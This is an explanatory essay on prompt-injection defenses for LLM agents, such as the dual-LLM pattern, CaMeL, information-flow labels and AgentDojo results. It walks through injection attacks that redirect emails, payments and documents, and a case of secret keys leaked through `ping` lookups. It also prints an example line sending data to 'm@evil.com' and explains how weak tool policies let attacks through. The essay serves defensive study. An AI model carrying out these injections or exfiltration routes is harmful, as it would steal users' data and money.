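# What design-enforced defenses against prompt injection assume

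## Prompt injection and the idea of enforcing safety outside the model

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model. The attacker places text in something the model will read, such as an email, a web page or a shared file, and the model treats that text as an instruction. The result is a bad answer if the software only displays the model's answers, but if it also lets the model send mail, move money or delete files, the attacker can do those things with the user's authority. *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Coker, 2026) reports that OWASP, a foundation that ranks software security risks, still places prompt injection first among the risks to language-model applications.

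Many defenses try to make the model, or a second model, recognise the attack. Others are built on the assumption that some attacks on the model will succeed, so they use ordinary code to allow or refuse each action. Designers can prove things about ordinary code that nobody can yet prove about a language model. But the proofs rest on assumptions, and most of the interesting disagreements about these systems are about those assumptions.

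### The tool loop

An agent is a program that runs a language model in a loop and offers it tools, which are functions such as "search the inbox" or "send a message". *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the usual loop. The program sends the model the conversation so far and a description of each tool. The model returns either a final answer or a request to call a tool with particular arguments. If it requests a tool, the program runs the tool, appends the result to the conversation and queries the model again, until the model gives a final answer.

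The model in this loop requests actions, such as sending an email, by outputting text in a recognisable format. The surrounding program carries out or rejects each request, so a check can run before anything is executed.

The loop is also the source of the weakness. The program marks each message with a role (system, user, assistant or tool), but it then joins all the messages into one string for the model, so a stranger's email ends up in the same text as the user's request. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written in December 2025 by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explains why this is hard to fix. It compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Developers solved SQL injection with parameterised queries, which set the structure of the command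 before the database fills in the user's input. This works because a database handles commands and values separately. A language model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the tokens before it, and nothing in that process separates instructions from data. If a job applicant hides "approve this CV" in a document, the model may therefore treat it as an instruction.

David C concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete fix like the one for SQL injection. The argument is based on how present models work and supported by the poor record of attempted fixes, but it does not prove that a complete fix is impossible.

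### Persuading the model or checking the action

*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) divides defenses by where they operate. In-band defenses work on the model or on the text it reads. Examples include training the model to ignore instructions in data, wrapping untrusted text in special delimiters, and running a classifier over every incoming document. Out-of-band defenses leave the model as it is and put a check between the model's request and the tool.

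In-band defenses reduce the number of successful attacks, but some still succeed. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) relays OpenAI's October 2026 score for injections arriving through outside content. If that score is a share of attempts, about three in a hundred got through. *FrontierBreach*, the security vendor PromptArmor's own benchmark, records successful attacks on frontier models from every provider. Training on more attacks does not reliably help, and *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) reports research in which it left agents easier to hijack.

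Small failure rates matter because an attacker can try again. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's results for an older model, Claude Opus 4.5, working as a coding agent. An automated attacker succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. Attackers who tailor their text to a known defense also succeed much more often than the attacks in fixed test sets.

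An out-of-band check examines the requested tool, its arguments and, in more elaborate systems, where those arguments came from. Rewording the malicious email does not by itself change the outcome, because the check does not evaluate the wording. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) goes further and treats the model as an operating system treats an arbitrary program, as a component that may do anything and that the rest of the system has to contain. Better model behaviour then leaves the check fewer bad actions to block, but the security argument does not depend on it.

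### Two models and a controller

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed an early design of this kind, which splits the assistant between two models. The planner, which Willison calls the privileged model, receives the user's request and can call tools. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. A controller between them, which is ordinary software, runs the tools, calls both models and stores the data.

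In Willison's worked example, a user requests a summary of their latest email, and the planner refers to the email and its summary only by variable names, without receiving any of the email's text. The controller passes the request to the planner, which responds with an instruction to fetch one email and store it as `$VAR1`. The controller fetches the email but does not send its contents to the planner. The planner then issues an instruction to run the quarantined model on the prompt "Summarize this: `$VAR1`". The controller substitutes the email's text for the variable, runs the quarantined model, saves the output as `$VAR2` and notifies the planner only that the summary is finished. The planner then instructs the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

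The design depends on keeping the quarantined model's output away from the planner, because a malicious email could cause the quarantined model to write a new injection into its summary. Willison allows one exception, for when the quarantined model only has to pick from a fixed set of categories. The controller can then confirm that the output is one of them and pass it to the planner. An attacker may still influence which category the model picks, but cannot get their own text to the planner.

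Willison proposed this design without proof or measurements, and he called the solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that lets untrusted text through to the planner undoes the protection. It also assumes that whatever the user types is trustworthy, so it doesn't block an injection in text the user pastes from a hostile web page.

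### The document for Bob

In 2025 a Google DeepMind paper introduced CaMeL, a more developed system of the same kind, and described a flaw in the two-model pattern. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, accepted the criticism and reproduced the paper's example. In it, a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that the meeting notes contain Bob's email address and the document's name.

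The planner can write the whole plan from that request alone:

1. Find the recent meeting notes.
2. Extract the name of the document.
3. Extract Bob's email address.
4. Fetch the document with that name.
5. Send it to that address.

The quarantined model reads the notes, since someone else may have written in them. Suppose an attacker has added a line telling any model that reads the file to give the attacker's address as Bob's. The quarantined model returns that address, and the controller stores it in a variable. The planner then orders the document sent to the address in the variable, so the document goes to the attacker.

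The assistant still followed the plan, calling the tools the planner chose in the order it chose, and the planner never saw the injected line. An attacker can change the document's name in the same way, because it comes from the same file. An attacker who controls both the recipient and the document's name can turn "send Bob this document" into "send any file in the drive to anyone".

The two-model pattern provides control-flow integrity, which means that every action that runs belongs to the plan made from the trusted request. It does not provide data-flow integrity, which requires that untrusted data cannot push the arguments or outcomes of permitted actions beyond what the user authorised. Similarly, a parameterised SQL query stops a form field from becoming a new command, but if the query sends a payment to whatever account number the field contains, the money can go to a thief's account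 unless something else checks the number.

The system could record that the address came from the notes and refuse untrusted recipients, but this would make the task impossible, because the user told the assistant to take the address from the notes. The system needs a way to treat this untrusted data as trusted for this purpose, which security researchers call endorsement. In Willison's account of CaMeL, if the recipient's address is already known and trusted, the system can send a message without asking the user, and otherwise it can ask for approval. Narisetty and colleagues regard tasks in which untrusted content must drive a consequential action as the deepest open problem for this family of defenses. That seems right, because separating two models, however strictly, will not determine whether an address in a file is really Bob's.

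### The reference monitor

The idea of a small, trustworthy checker around untrustworthy programs is much older than language models. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report to the US Air Force, dealt with computers shared by people with different security clearances. Its central proposal was a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, devices or other programs against a list of what its user may do. Anderson required that the monitor be tamper-proof, that the system invoke it every time, and that it be small enough to analyse and test completely.

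Anderson applied these requirements to a Honeywell computer of the period. Its hardware acted as a kind of reference monitor by confining each user's program to its own area of memory. But the operating system, which did essential work on the program's behalf, mostly ran with that confinement switched off, so the check was not always invoked. Counting the operating system as part of the monitor would have brought the monitor to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify.

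In an agent, the monitor sits where tool calls take effect, and the same three requirements can help identify weaknesses. Narisetty and colleagues class a side channel, which reveals a secret through behaviour such as errors or timing, as a failure to check everything. Having a language model write the monitor's rules makes it harder to meet the requirement that people can verify the mechanism. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists what must work correctly for a guarantee to hold, called the trusted base. It includes the host operating system, the isolation mechanisms, the monitor and the policy that determines which calls may run. If the system labels data, the labels and the code that handles them are also part of the trusted base.

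The policy deserves particular suspicion because even a perfect monitor will enforce a bad rule. The same paper describes an attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Claude Code required human approval for many commands that could send data to unknown domains, but not for `ping`, which tests whether another computer is reachable. Instructions hidden in a code file could make the agent read secret keys and pass them to `ping` as part of a domain name. Looking up that name sent the keys to the attacker's server.

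### Labels for trust and secrecy

To enforce data-flow integrity, a monitor must track where each value came from. *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) supplied the mathematics that most later systems use. Every piece of data belongs to a security class, and a relation between classes determines which way information may flow. When a program combines two values, the result belongs to the lowest class that both inputs may flow into, known as their join. Classes related in this way form a lattice.

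Costa and colleagues, who built a system called FIDES on this basis, start from two properties, integrity (trusted or untrusted) and confidentiality (public or secret). Together they make four labels, shown here with typical examples.

| | Public | Secret |
|---|---|---|
| **Trusted** | The user's request | A record from the company database |
| **Untrusted** | A page from the open web | A stranger's email in a private inbox |

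Trusted, public data can flow anywhere in this lattice. Untrusted, secret data can flow only to places with the same label. Taint tracking passes labels from inputs to outputs. When inputs are combined, a join takes the more restrictive value for both secrecy and trust, so a paragraph based on the database record and the web page is secret because of the record and untrusted because of the page.

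Language models make taint tracking imprecise. In an ordinary program, one can often see that a result depends on one input and not on another. Anything in a model's context can affect its output, so the safe course is to give the output the join of all the labels the model read. A single untrusted email in the conversation then taints every later request the model makes. Keeping the email in a variable, as Willison's controller does, avoids this because the variable carries its own label and the planner's context stays untainted.

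In the example of Bob's document, the address is labeled "untrusted" because it came from the notes. A policy that requires a trusted recipient would stop the attack, but it would also block the delivery if nobody had tampered with the notes and the address were Bob's real one. A label records only a value's origin, so it can't show whether the value is correct.

### Copied secrets and inferred secrets

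Confidentiality labels raise a further difficulty, which Denning illustrated with one line of code: `if a = 0 then b := 0`. Suppose `a` is secret, `b` is public, and `b` starts out nonzero. The line never copies `a` into `b`, but anyone who looks at `b` afterwards can tell whether `a` was zero, because `b` changes only if it was. When `a` is not zero, the program leaks that fact without executing the assignment. Denning called this an implicit flow, in contrast to the explicit flow of copying a value or computing with it.

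Agents do the same thing whenever they base a decision on private data. For example, a user might ask an assistant to read a confidential medical result and, if it is positive, look up a particular specialist's public website. The text of the result never leaves the inbox, but anyone who reads the website's logs can still draw a conclusion from the visit.

Noninterference rules this out by requiring that changing the secret inputs does not affect anything an outside observer can see. Explicit secrecy is weaker. It requires only that secrets are not copied to public places, though the choice of actions may still reveal something about them. The assistant in the medical example satisfies explicit secrecy but violates noninterference.

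Costa and colleagues chose explicit secrecy over noninterference because, they argue, noninterference would essentially forbid an agent to use any tool with publicly visible effects after a tool that may read secrets. An assistant under that rule could do very little. Their proof therefore does not cover timing or what an observer can infer from the order of tool calls. A version of noninterference for trust, which requires that changing untrusted inputs not affect trusted outputs, would be just as restrictive for an assistant whose job is to react to incoming mail.

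### How AgentDojo measures attacks

Most of the measurements for these systems come from *AgentDojo*, a benchmark that Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) built from simulated applications. It has four suites, each with its own tools, ordinary user tasks and attacker's goals, called injection tasks.

| Suite | User tasks | Injection tasks | Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 40 | 6 | 240 |
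| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |

Pairing every user task with every injection task in the same suite gives 629 security cases. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) later reports more than 900 combinations, so results from different years may not cover the same cases.

In each case, the benchmark places the attacker's text where an outsider could plausibly have put it, such as the body of an email, while the agent works on the user's task. Code then inspects the state of the simulated applications. If the attacker wanted money sent to a certain account, the code checks for that transfer. The designers did not use a language model as the judge because a good injection might hijack the judge as well.

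AgentDojo reports three metrics. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. This metric helps identify agents that are secure only because they refuse every task. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which the agent completes the user's task with no malicious side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker achieves their goal.

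GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024, carried out the attacker's goal in 47.7% of cases when the injection addressed the model and the user by their correct names. When Debenedetti and colleagues made the model select the tools it would need before it read any untrusted data, and removed the rest, the rate fell to 7.5%. Much of that gain came from cases where the user's task only required reading but the attack required sending or writing. In 17% of the test cases, however, the tools for the user's task were also enough for the attack. Bob's document is such a case, because the assistant needs the tool that the attacker wants to misuse.

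A low attack success rate on AgentDojo does not necessarily mean that a system is secure. Narisetty and colleagues ran a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, with no defense on a sample of the workspace tasks and recorded an attack success rate of zero. In the run they inspected, the injected text reached the model, which answered the user's question and did nothing else. The zero reflected a weak model and mostly read-only tasks. Anderson had already pointed out a more general limit of such testing when discussing the "tiger teams" that tried to break into computers in the 1970s. Such a team can reveal flaws, but if it finds none, the security of the system is still unknown. For this reason, AgentDojo's designers intended others to add new attacks, and a good result against the original attacks shows resistance only to those.

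### What a guarantee of this kind promises

Unlike a benchmark, a proof can cover attacks that nobody has thought of yet, but it holds only under certain conditions. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) is unusually direct about its conditions. Its agent acts by writing programs, and a type checker rejects any program that breaks the rules before it can run. The paper proves that if the programming language enforces a property for every program that passes the checker, and all of the agent's code must pass, then the property holds for the entire system. The proof does not show that the developer picked the right property.

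The other systems offer the same kind of conditional guarantee. A stated class of harm cannot occur if the policies, labels, trusted inputs, approvals and interpreter (the code that executes the plan and carries the labels along) are sound. If any one of these is flawed, the attacker could still get Bob's document, even though the theorem remains true. The policy might permit mail to any address. Someone might have labelled the meeting notes as trusted because they sit on the company's own drive. The interpreter might lose the label when it copies the address from one variable to another. The request itself might be text that the user pasted from a hostile message, or the user might approve the unfamiliar recipient without reading the address.

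The harms these defenses cover are also limited, normally to forbidden actions and forbidden flows of data, which leaves out harm done by text alone. In the two-model pattern, the quarantined model summarises a hostile email and the controller displays the summary. If the email makes the summary false, the system has still broken no rule. Debenedetti and colleagues give the example of a hotel listing with an injection that makes the model always recommend that hotel. Isolating the planner does not help, because the user asked for a recommendation. Costa and colleagues treat replies to the user as inconsequential by default, but note that a system could check those too.

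An injection can also trick the user into leaking private data. Willison describes one that makes the assistant encode the data as a meaningless-looking string and invite the user to paste it into a website in exchange for a funny picture of a monkey. A monitor on tool calls cannot block this leak because the user sends the data.

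## CaMeL: a fixed plan, tagged values and hand-written policies

CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", keeps the planner and the quarantined model of the two-model pattern. It also records where each value came from and checks that record before any tool runs, which the system in the example of Bob's document did not do.

### From a request to a program

CaMeL's planner writes a whole program in a restricted form of Python before any tool runs, whereas the planner in the two-model pattern issues one instruction at a time. Willison reports that the designers chose Python because language models already write it well. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), who extend CaMeL in *CaMeLoT*, note that the restricted language leaves out arbitrary `while` loops and some other constructs that make a program hard to analyse. An interpreter built for CaMeL parses the program into a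 syntax tree, in which every assignment, function call and condition is a node, and executes it node by node, tracking which values came from which others.

The program calls both tools and the quarantined model as functions. It passes the quarantined model a question, some data and the type of answer it must return, such as an email address, and the interpreter stores the answer in a variable. Extracting an address is easier than writing a plan, so the quarantined model can be a smaller model that runs on the user's computer. The company that hosts the planner would then receive the user's request but none of the user's emails or files.

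CaMeL's planner writes its program in advance, so it needs a description of how each tool's output is structured. An ordinary agent can call a tool and infer the structure from its output. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which applies CaMeL to groups of agents, points out that CaMeL's planner has to write the code that parses an output before the tool has returned one. AgentDojo's default tool descriptions don't specify the structure of outputs, so the researchers added it, as DeepMind's researchers had done for the original evaluation. Adding it is a modest, one-time job for a fixed set of tools, but CaMeL's benchmark scores depend on it.

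The tags on a value, together called its capability, record where the value came from (its sources) and who may see it (its readers). Some tags depend on facts available only when a tool runs. In an example from Nikolaou and colleagues, the readers of a calendar event are the user and the people invited, and its description is trusted only if the user wrote it. A value that the program computes inherits the tags of everything that went into it.

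Each time the program tries to call a tool, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, which is also a Python function. The policy receives the call, its arguments and their capabilities, and returns a decision to allow or deny the call, along with a reason. The three-line policy for changing a bank password allows the change only if the new password is trusted.

### The email reminder, line by line

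In a short example from Willison, the user asks the assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting. The planner writes a program of three statements.

`email = get_last_email()`

This call is always allowed because it only reads. The interpreter stores the message in `email` and records the inbox as its source. The value is untrusted, since anyone could have sent the message.

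`address = query_quarantined_llm("Find Bob's email address in [email]", output_schema=EmailStr)`

The quarantined model reads the message and must answer with an email address. That requirement stops it from returning a paragraph of injected instructions, but the attacker's address is also a valid email address. The interpreter computed `address` from `email`, so `address` is untrusted too.

`send_email(recipient=address, subject="Meeting tomorrow", ...)`

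The planner wrote the subject and body from the user's request alone, so both are trusted, but the recipient is not. Before sending the reminder, the interpreter runs the policy for `send_email`, which in this example requires a trusted recipient. The reminder goes out only if the address is already known and trusted or the user approves it.

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reproduces this example with an attack. The email ends with a fake postscript in Bob's name, saying he has to cancel and asking for a cancellation note instead of the reminder. An ordinary tool-calling agent sends the cancellation. An agent that wrote its program before opening the email sends the reminder, because the program already contains the reminder's wording.

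They also use a different policy for `send_email`, which requires the subject and body to be trusted but accepts any recipient. The program therefore runs without interrupting the user, and the email can't affect what the reminder says, but it can still determine who receives it. The policy in Willison's example is also sensible. It prevents an attacker from redirecting the message, but a legitimate email from a new contact leads to a refusal or a request for approval.

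### The published results

Aktagon's *CaMeL* (2026), a summary of the DeepMind paper, reports that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. With Gemini 2.5 Pro as the model, successful attacks fell from 300 to zero.

The DeepMind evaluation recorded two successful injections, which Garby and colleagues describe. In one, a user asked the agent to make a payment as directed by a document that an attacker controlled. The DeepMind researchers place this case outside their threat model. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo's check counted the attacker's text in the quotation as a successful injection.

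CaMeL uses more tokens than an undefended agent. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that the median AgentDojo task takes 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens with GPT-4o, excluding the text that describes the tools. The overhead can be much higher for agents that operate a desktop computer. On 17 such tasks, *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports about 456,000 output tokens with CaMeL and 13,000 without any defense, largely because the plan has to cover everything the agent might find on the screen.

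A later test by another group found similar security but a lower task completion rate than the published 77%. *CapLite* (2026), which presents a cheaper defense for small models, tested CaMeL on 15 models, and 20 of 13,935 attacks succeeded. CaMeL used 93,700 tokens per episode, against 28,000 for the undefended agent. The paper's figures imply that CaMeL completed only about 27% of user tasks under attack. The models and set-ups differ, so this does not refute the published figure, but users clearly can't expect 77% from every model.

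Aktagon's summary also describes the 77% as tasks solved with "provable security", but CaMeL has no theorem comparable to those for some later systems. Garby and colleagues report that the DeepMind paper lists formalisation as future work and that the only full definition of how tags spread is the interpreter's Python code. They also found cases in which the interpreter fails to track a value's source.

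### What the plan stops and what the policies stop

CaMeL's headline figures combine the effects of two defenses, the fixed plan and the policies. To separate them, Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking suite with policy checks on and off. With the checks off, the planner still writes its program before it can see any untrusted text, but every tool call runs regardless of the tags on its arguments.

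The suite has 144 pairs of a user task and an attack. In 97 of them, the attack needs a tool call or file that the user's task doesn't require. For example, a program that summarises recent transactions contains no call to `send_money`, and text hidden in a transaction can't add one. The plan alone should defeat these attacks. In the other 47 pairs, the program may already contain what the attacker needs. If the user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a file, the program must call `send_money`, and the attacker only has to change the payment details.

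Garby and colleagues ran each user task and each pair three times with two models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. A full set would be 48 runs without an attack and 432 with one (291 from the 97 pairs and 141 from the 47). Many of the attacked runs never completed, and the table includes only those that did.

| Model and policies | Tasks solved, no attack | Tasks solved under attack | Attacks resisted, 97 pairs | Attacks resisted, 47 pairs |
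|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2, off | 32/48 (66.7%) | 96/135 (71.1%) | 98/99 | 141/141 |
| MiMo-v2.5, off | 34/48 (70.8%) | 104/144 (72.2%) | 240/241 | 138/141 |
| GPT-5.2, on | 18/48 (37.5%) | 70/233 (30.0%) | 97/97 | 134/134 |
| MiMo-v2.5, on | 18/48 (37.5%) | 148/357 (41.5%) | 216/216 | 141/141 |

On this benchmark, the policies prevented very few attacks. Five of 622 completed attacks succeeded with policies off, and none of 588 succeeded with policies on. With policies on, the share of tasks solved when there was no attack also fell by almost half, from around two thirds to 37.5%. The margins are wide because the suite has only 16 distinct user tasks (the 95% interval around 37.5% is about 27 points either way), and the missing runs could change the security figures.

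In the last column, 279 of 282 attacks failed without a policy, which is surprising because only a policy was supposed to stop them. They probably failed because AgentDojo's attack texts mostly tell the model to do something, such as transfer money, and a quarantined model without tools cannot do it. To exploit CaMeL's program, the attacker has to make the quarantined model return a particular wrong value in the format that the program expects. An attacker who knew that the target used CaMeL would write the injection to do this, as in the example of Bob's document. The policies-off results are therefore weak evidence of how CaMeL would fare without policies against such an attacker.

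### A program that obeys a file

Two of the five successful attacks came from the 97 pairs in which the plan should have been enough. Both involved the same user task, which asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely.

The planner could not see the file, so it did not know which tools the instructions would require. It dealt with this by writing a loop that could carry out any of them. In outline, a program of this kind looks like this:

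```
steps = query_quarantined_llm("List the steps in [file]", output_schema=list[Step])
for step in steps:
    if step.tool == "send_money":
        send_money(recipient=step.recipient, amount=step.amount)
    elif step.tool == "update_password":
        update_password(password=step.password)
    # ...and so on for each tool
```

Here the planner has rebuilt the ordinary tool loop inside its own program, which contains a call to every tool and lets the file determine which ones run and with what arguments. Whoever controls the file has about as much power as they would over an agent with no defense. The agent still has control-flow integrity in the literal sense, because every tool call belongs to a program that the planner wrote from the trusted request.

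Policies can stop this attack because the recipient and the password come from the file, which makes them untrusted. With policies on, the attack failed in every completed run in this group. With policies off, the fixed plan protects the user only if the request is specific enough for the planner to choose the actions itself. A request such as "do whatever this document says" lets the document's contents determine the actions, even if the planner never reads untrusted text.

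### Who writes the policies

Somebody has to write a policy for every tool that can do harm. The DeepMind paper acknowledges that users must specify and maintain these policies. This worries Willison, who still hasn't fully figured out the permission system of Amazon's cloud service after two decades of involvement in application security. Companies can assign the work to engineers, but a large organisation may have hundreds of tools. In *Operationalizing CaMeL*, Tallam and Miller (2025) expect that writing separate Python functions for each tool would lead to duplicated and inconsistent rules that nobody audits as a whole. They work at a security company and recommend keeping shared rules in one place, written in a language designed for access policies.

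The banking policies that Garby and colleagues wrote for their own agent show how easily a policy can be too loose. They are a deliberately simplified version of CaMeL's:

| Tool | What the policy requires |
|---|---|
| `send_money` | The recipient is trusted, and the recipient may read the amount, subject and date |
| `schedule_transaction` | The amount is trusted |
| `update_scheduled_transaction` | The recipient and the amount are trusted |
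| `update_password` | The new password is trusted |

As listed, the rule for `send_money` prevents an attacker from redirecting a payment but not from changing its size. If an attacker changes this month's rent in a file to ten times the usual figure, and the landlord's account is already trusted, the payment goes through. The rule for `schedule_transaction` has the opposite gap, since it checks the amount but accepts a recipient from any source. Both gaps are in the policies rather than the data tracking, so whoever writes a policy has to consider what an attacker could do with each argument of each tool.

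Rules about the text of commands are looser still. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a coding agent whose rules forbid it to read a certain file. If the agent may run Python, it can open the file with a one-line program, and a rule that matches shell commands will not detect this.

Policies that are safe individually can also be unsafe together. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on AI agents and defenses against them, lists combinations of individually permitted flows among CaMeL's remaining weaknesses. For instance, one policy might let the agent save text from a web page to a shared company folder, and another might treat everything in that folder as trusted. An attacker's text could then become trusted through two permitted steps.

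Overly strict policies cause a different problem, which shows up when nobody is attacking. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5 on all 97 AgentDojo user tasks, without injections. Their results imply the following outcomes.

| Suite | Tasks | Solved | Blocked by a policy | Allowed, but did not do the task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Slack | 21 | 6 | 10 | 5 |
| Banking | 16 | 6 | 8 | 2 |
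| Travel | 20 | 9 | 1 | 10 |
| Workspace | 40 | 28 | 7 | 5 |

The policies blocked 26 legitimate tasks, 18 of them in the Slack and banking suites. In banking, CaMeL solved 6 of 16 tasks (37.5%), the same share that Garby and colleagues recorded with two other models. A better model would probably not help much there, because the policies refuse half the tasks regardless of the model's ability. In the travel suite, the policies blocked almost nothing, and most failures came from programs that didn't do what the user wanted.

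Tallam and Miller cite an earlier overall completion rate of 67% and blame many of CaMeL's failures on rules that treat all untrusted data as equally dangerous. They propose three tiers: reading open data would need only a basic check of its source, changing the user's own files would need a quick confirmation if an argument was untrusted, and irreversible actions such as payments would need the full check and stronger approval. They did not test this on CaMeL, and it would do little for the banking tasks, since paying a bill belongs in the strictest tier.

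### Tasks that no safe policy allows

A better interpreter or more careful rules might let the agent complete the blocked tasks. TypeGuard, a system by Zhou and colleagues, is a useful comparison. It implements language-based agent control in Haskell, a programming language whose type system can restrict what a program may do as well as what data it handles.

In one TypeGuard example, an agent compiles a bibliography in which every entry must come from a trusted database. The only function that writes to the bibliography accepts entries of a special type, and the program can only get a value of that type by fetching it from the database, so the compiler rejects any program that tries to write an invented entry. TypeGuard relies on an existing Haskell library to control the flow of untrusted and secret data. The library keeps a label for the whole running computation. Reading a web page adds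 the page's source to that label, and writing later to a destination that requires more trusted data causes an error.

Zhou and colleagues translated CaMeL's policies for the Slack suite into this library and ran both systems with GPT-5.4. Without policies, each system solved 15 of the 21 user tasks. With policies, TypeGuard solved 8 and CaMeL solved 7, and both resisted all 105 injections under each of two kinds of attack. The two systems lost about the same number of tasks even though they enforce the policies in very different ways, which suggests that most of the loss comes from the policies and the tasks, not from how CaMeL enforces the policies.

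Zhou and colleagues' explanation is that many Slack tasks involve "flows that no secure policy would admit". One such task is to forward the contents of an untrusted channel to a user mentioned in the task's data. If outsiders can write in the channel, they may supply both the text and the choice of recipient. As with Bob's document, a policy based on where the data came from must either allow both the honest request and the attack or refuse both.

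Paying the bill described in a file raises the same problem, and both kinds of task need some form of endorsement. CaMeL can ask the user to approve the blocked call, which works only if people read what they approve. Garby and colleagues' agent lets the planner endorse particular values in its program before the planner has seen any untrusted data.

A later version of Zhou and colleagues' work, which renames the system ELBA, shows that CaMeL's fixed plan also limits how many tasks it solves. With policies on, ELBA solved 8 to 10 of the Slack tasks, depending on which of four models it used, while CaMeL solved 4 to 6 with the same models. ELBA's agents can adapt to what they find by writing further programs after they have seen some data, but they took about three times as long as CaMeL.

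This flexibility makes the policies more important, because ELBA lets untrusted text reach a component that writes code. That exposure made little difference on AgentDojo's standard attacks, and both ELBA and CaMeL resisted every injection in the Slack suite even without policies. But in a separate adversarial evaluation, ELBA resisted only 58% to 85% of injections without policies, depending on the model, and all of them with policies. This is better evidence for the value of policies than the banking reruns, in which almost every attack failed anyway.

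### Checking the program before it runs

CaMeL checks each policy when the tool is called, so a program may read many emails and query the quarantined model about each one before a policy blocks its last step. By then the program has used tokens and may have changed something. CaMeLoT, an extension of CaMeL by Nikolaou and colleagues, examines the whole program before any tool runs.

CaMeLoT translates the program into a state machine, a map of the points the program can reach and the possible steps between them. The map includes both branches of each condition and allows any number of repetitions of each loop. CaMeLoT marks every variable as coming from the program's own text, the user's query, a tool's output or the quarantined model. A value computed from several others takes the least trusted of their marks. A model checker, which examines every path through the map, then tests rules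 such as one that a direct message goes only to a trusted recipient. If a path breaks a rule, CaMeLoT describes that path to the planner, which rewrites the program. This repeats until a version passes or the attempts run out.

The email reminder would fail this check. Nikolaou and colleagues use a nearly identical program, which extracts Bob's address from a chat channel and sends him a message, and the model checker rejects it before the agent has read anything. Rewriting the program helps if there is another way to get the address, such as a directory that is trusted under the policies. If the channel is the only source of Bob's address, no rewritten program can pass, and checking earlier only saves the work the agent would have done before being refused.

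CaMeLoT fully reproduces the trust requirements of 22 of the 28 CaMeL policies for tools with side effects. The other six depend on facts that do not exist until the program runs, such as who has access to a shared file at that moment. CaMeLoT also leaves secrecy to CaMeL, because the readers of a value are often unknown in advance. When it cannot determine whether a value is trusted, it treats the value as untrusted, so it rejects some safe programs. In 22 AgentDojo tasks, the program ran under both systems but did the wrong thing. Of the other 75, the two systems reached the same decision in 59. In seven, CaMeLoT rejected a program that CaMeL allowed, and in nine it accepted a program that CaMeL went on to block, so CaMeL's checks during execution are still necessary.

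CaMeLoT adds rules about the order of events. A CaMeL policy considers one call at a time, so it has no natural way to require that a person approve isolating a computer from the network before the agent does it, or that the agent eventually close every incident ticket it opens. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven rules for a security team's agent, mostly of this kind, and a faulty plan to break each one. CaMeLoT caught all seven plans, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. They expected this result because they chose rules that go beyond what CaMeL can express.

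A language model also derived extra rules from the user's request, so that CaMeLoT could reject a program that was safe but did not do the job. The model identified exactly the right set of state-changing tools for 85 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks. For the other 12, a missing rule could let an incomplete program pass, and an invented rule could block a good program.

The model checker proves that the state machine obeys the rules on every path. That proof applies to the running agent only if the translation from Python keeps all the behaviour that matters and the marks on the tools' outputs are correct. The rules themselves still come from a person or a model. If a rule for payments checks the recipient but not the amount, CaMeLoT will approve a program that pays the landlord the wrong rent.

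## Leaks through CaMeL's interpreter: branches, errors, retries and timing

A CaMeL policy is only as reliable as the tags it checks. The interpreter computes these tags line by line as the program runs, and they are supposed to record everything that influenced a value. Tracking that influence is straightforward when the program copies a value or computes with it, but much harder when private or untrusted data determines which lines run, because the data then affects values that are not copied or computed from it.

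### Normal and strict mode

CaMeL's interpreter has two modes. In normal mode, a value inherits tags only from the data used to compute it. Strict mode also tracks control dependencies, according to *PolicySniff* (2026), a paper that describes a hardware timing attack and reviews the leaks CaMeL's designers reported. Whatever the program does inside an `if` statement then inherits the tags of the condition.

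Garby and colleagues give an example that shows why this matters:

`if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")`

Anyone who receives the email learns that the balance is above the threshold. Tracking the data alone misses this leak, because both arguments are constants in the program and are therefore trusted and public. This is an implicit flow of the kind Denning described. To catch it, an interpreter can keep a label for the program's current position, called the program-counter label. Because the balance is secret, the interpreter marks the position as secret when the program enters the branch, and treats the email as secret too. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL refuses to send it.

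Strict mode also blocks harmless actions. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Carol a specific agenda if Bob's latest email says the meeting has moved. The program uses the quarantined model to check whether the email says this, and sends the agenda if it does. Bob's email cannot change the agenda or the recipient. But in strict mode, the `send_email` call inherits the email's tags, which mark it as untrusted and not readable by Carol. A policy that checks either property will block the message or require the user's approval.

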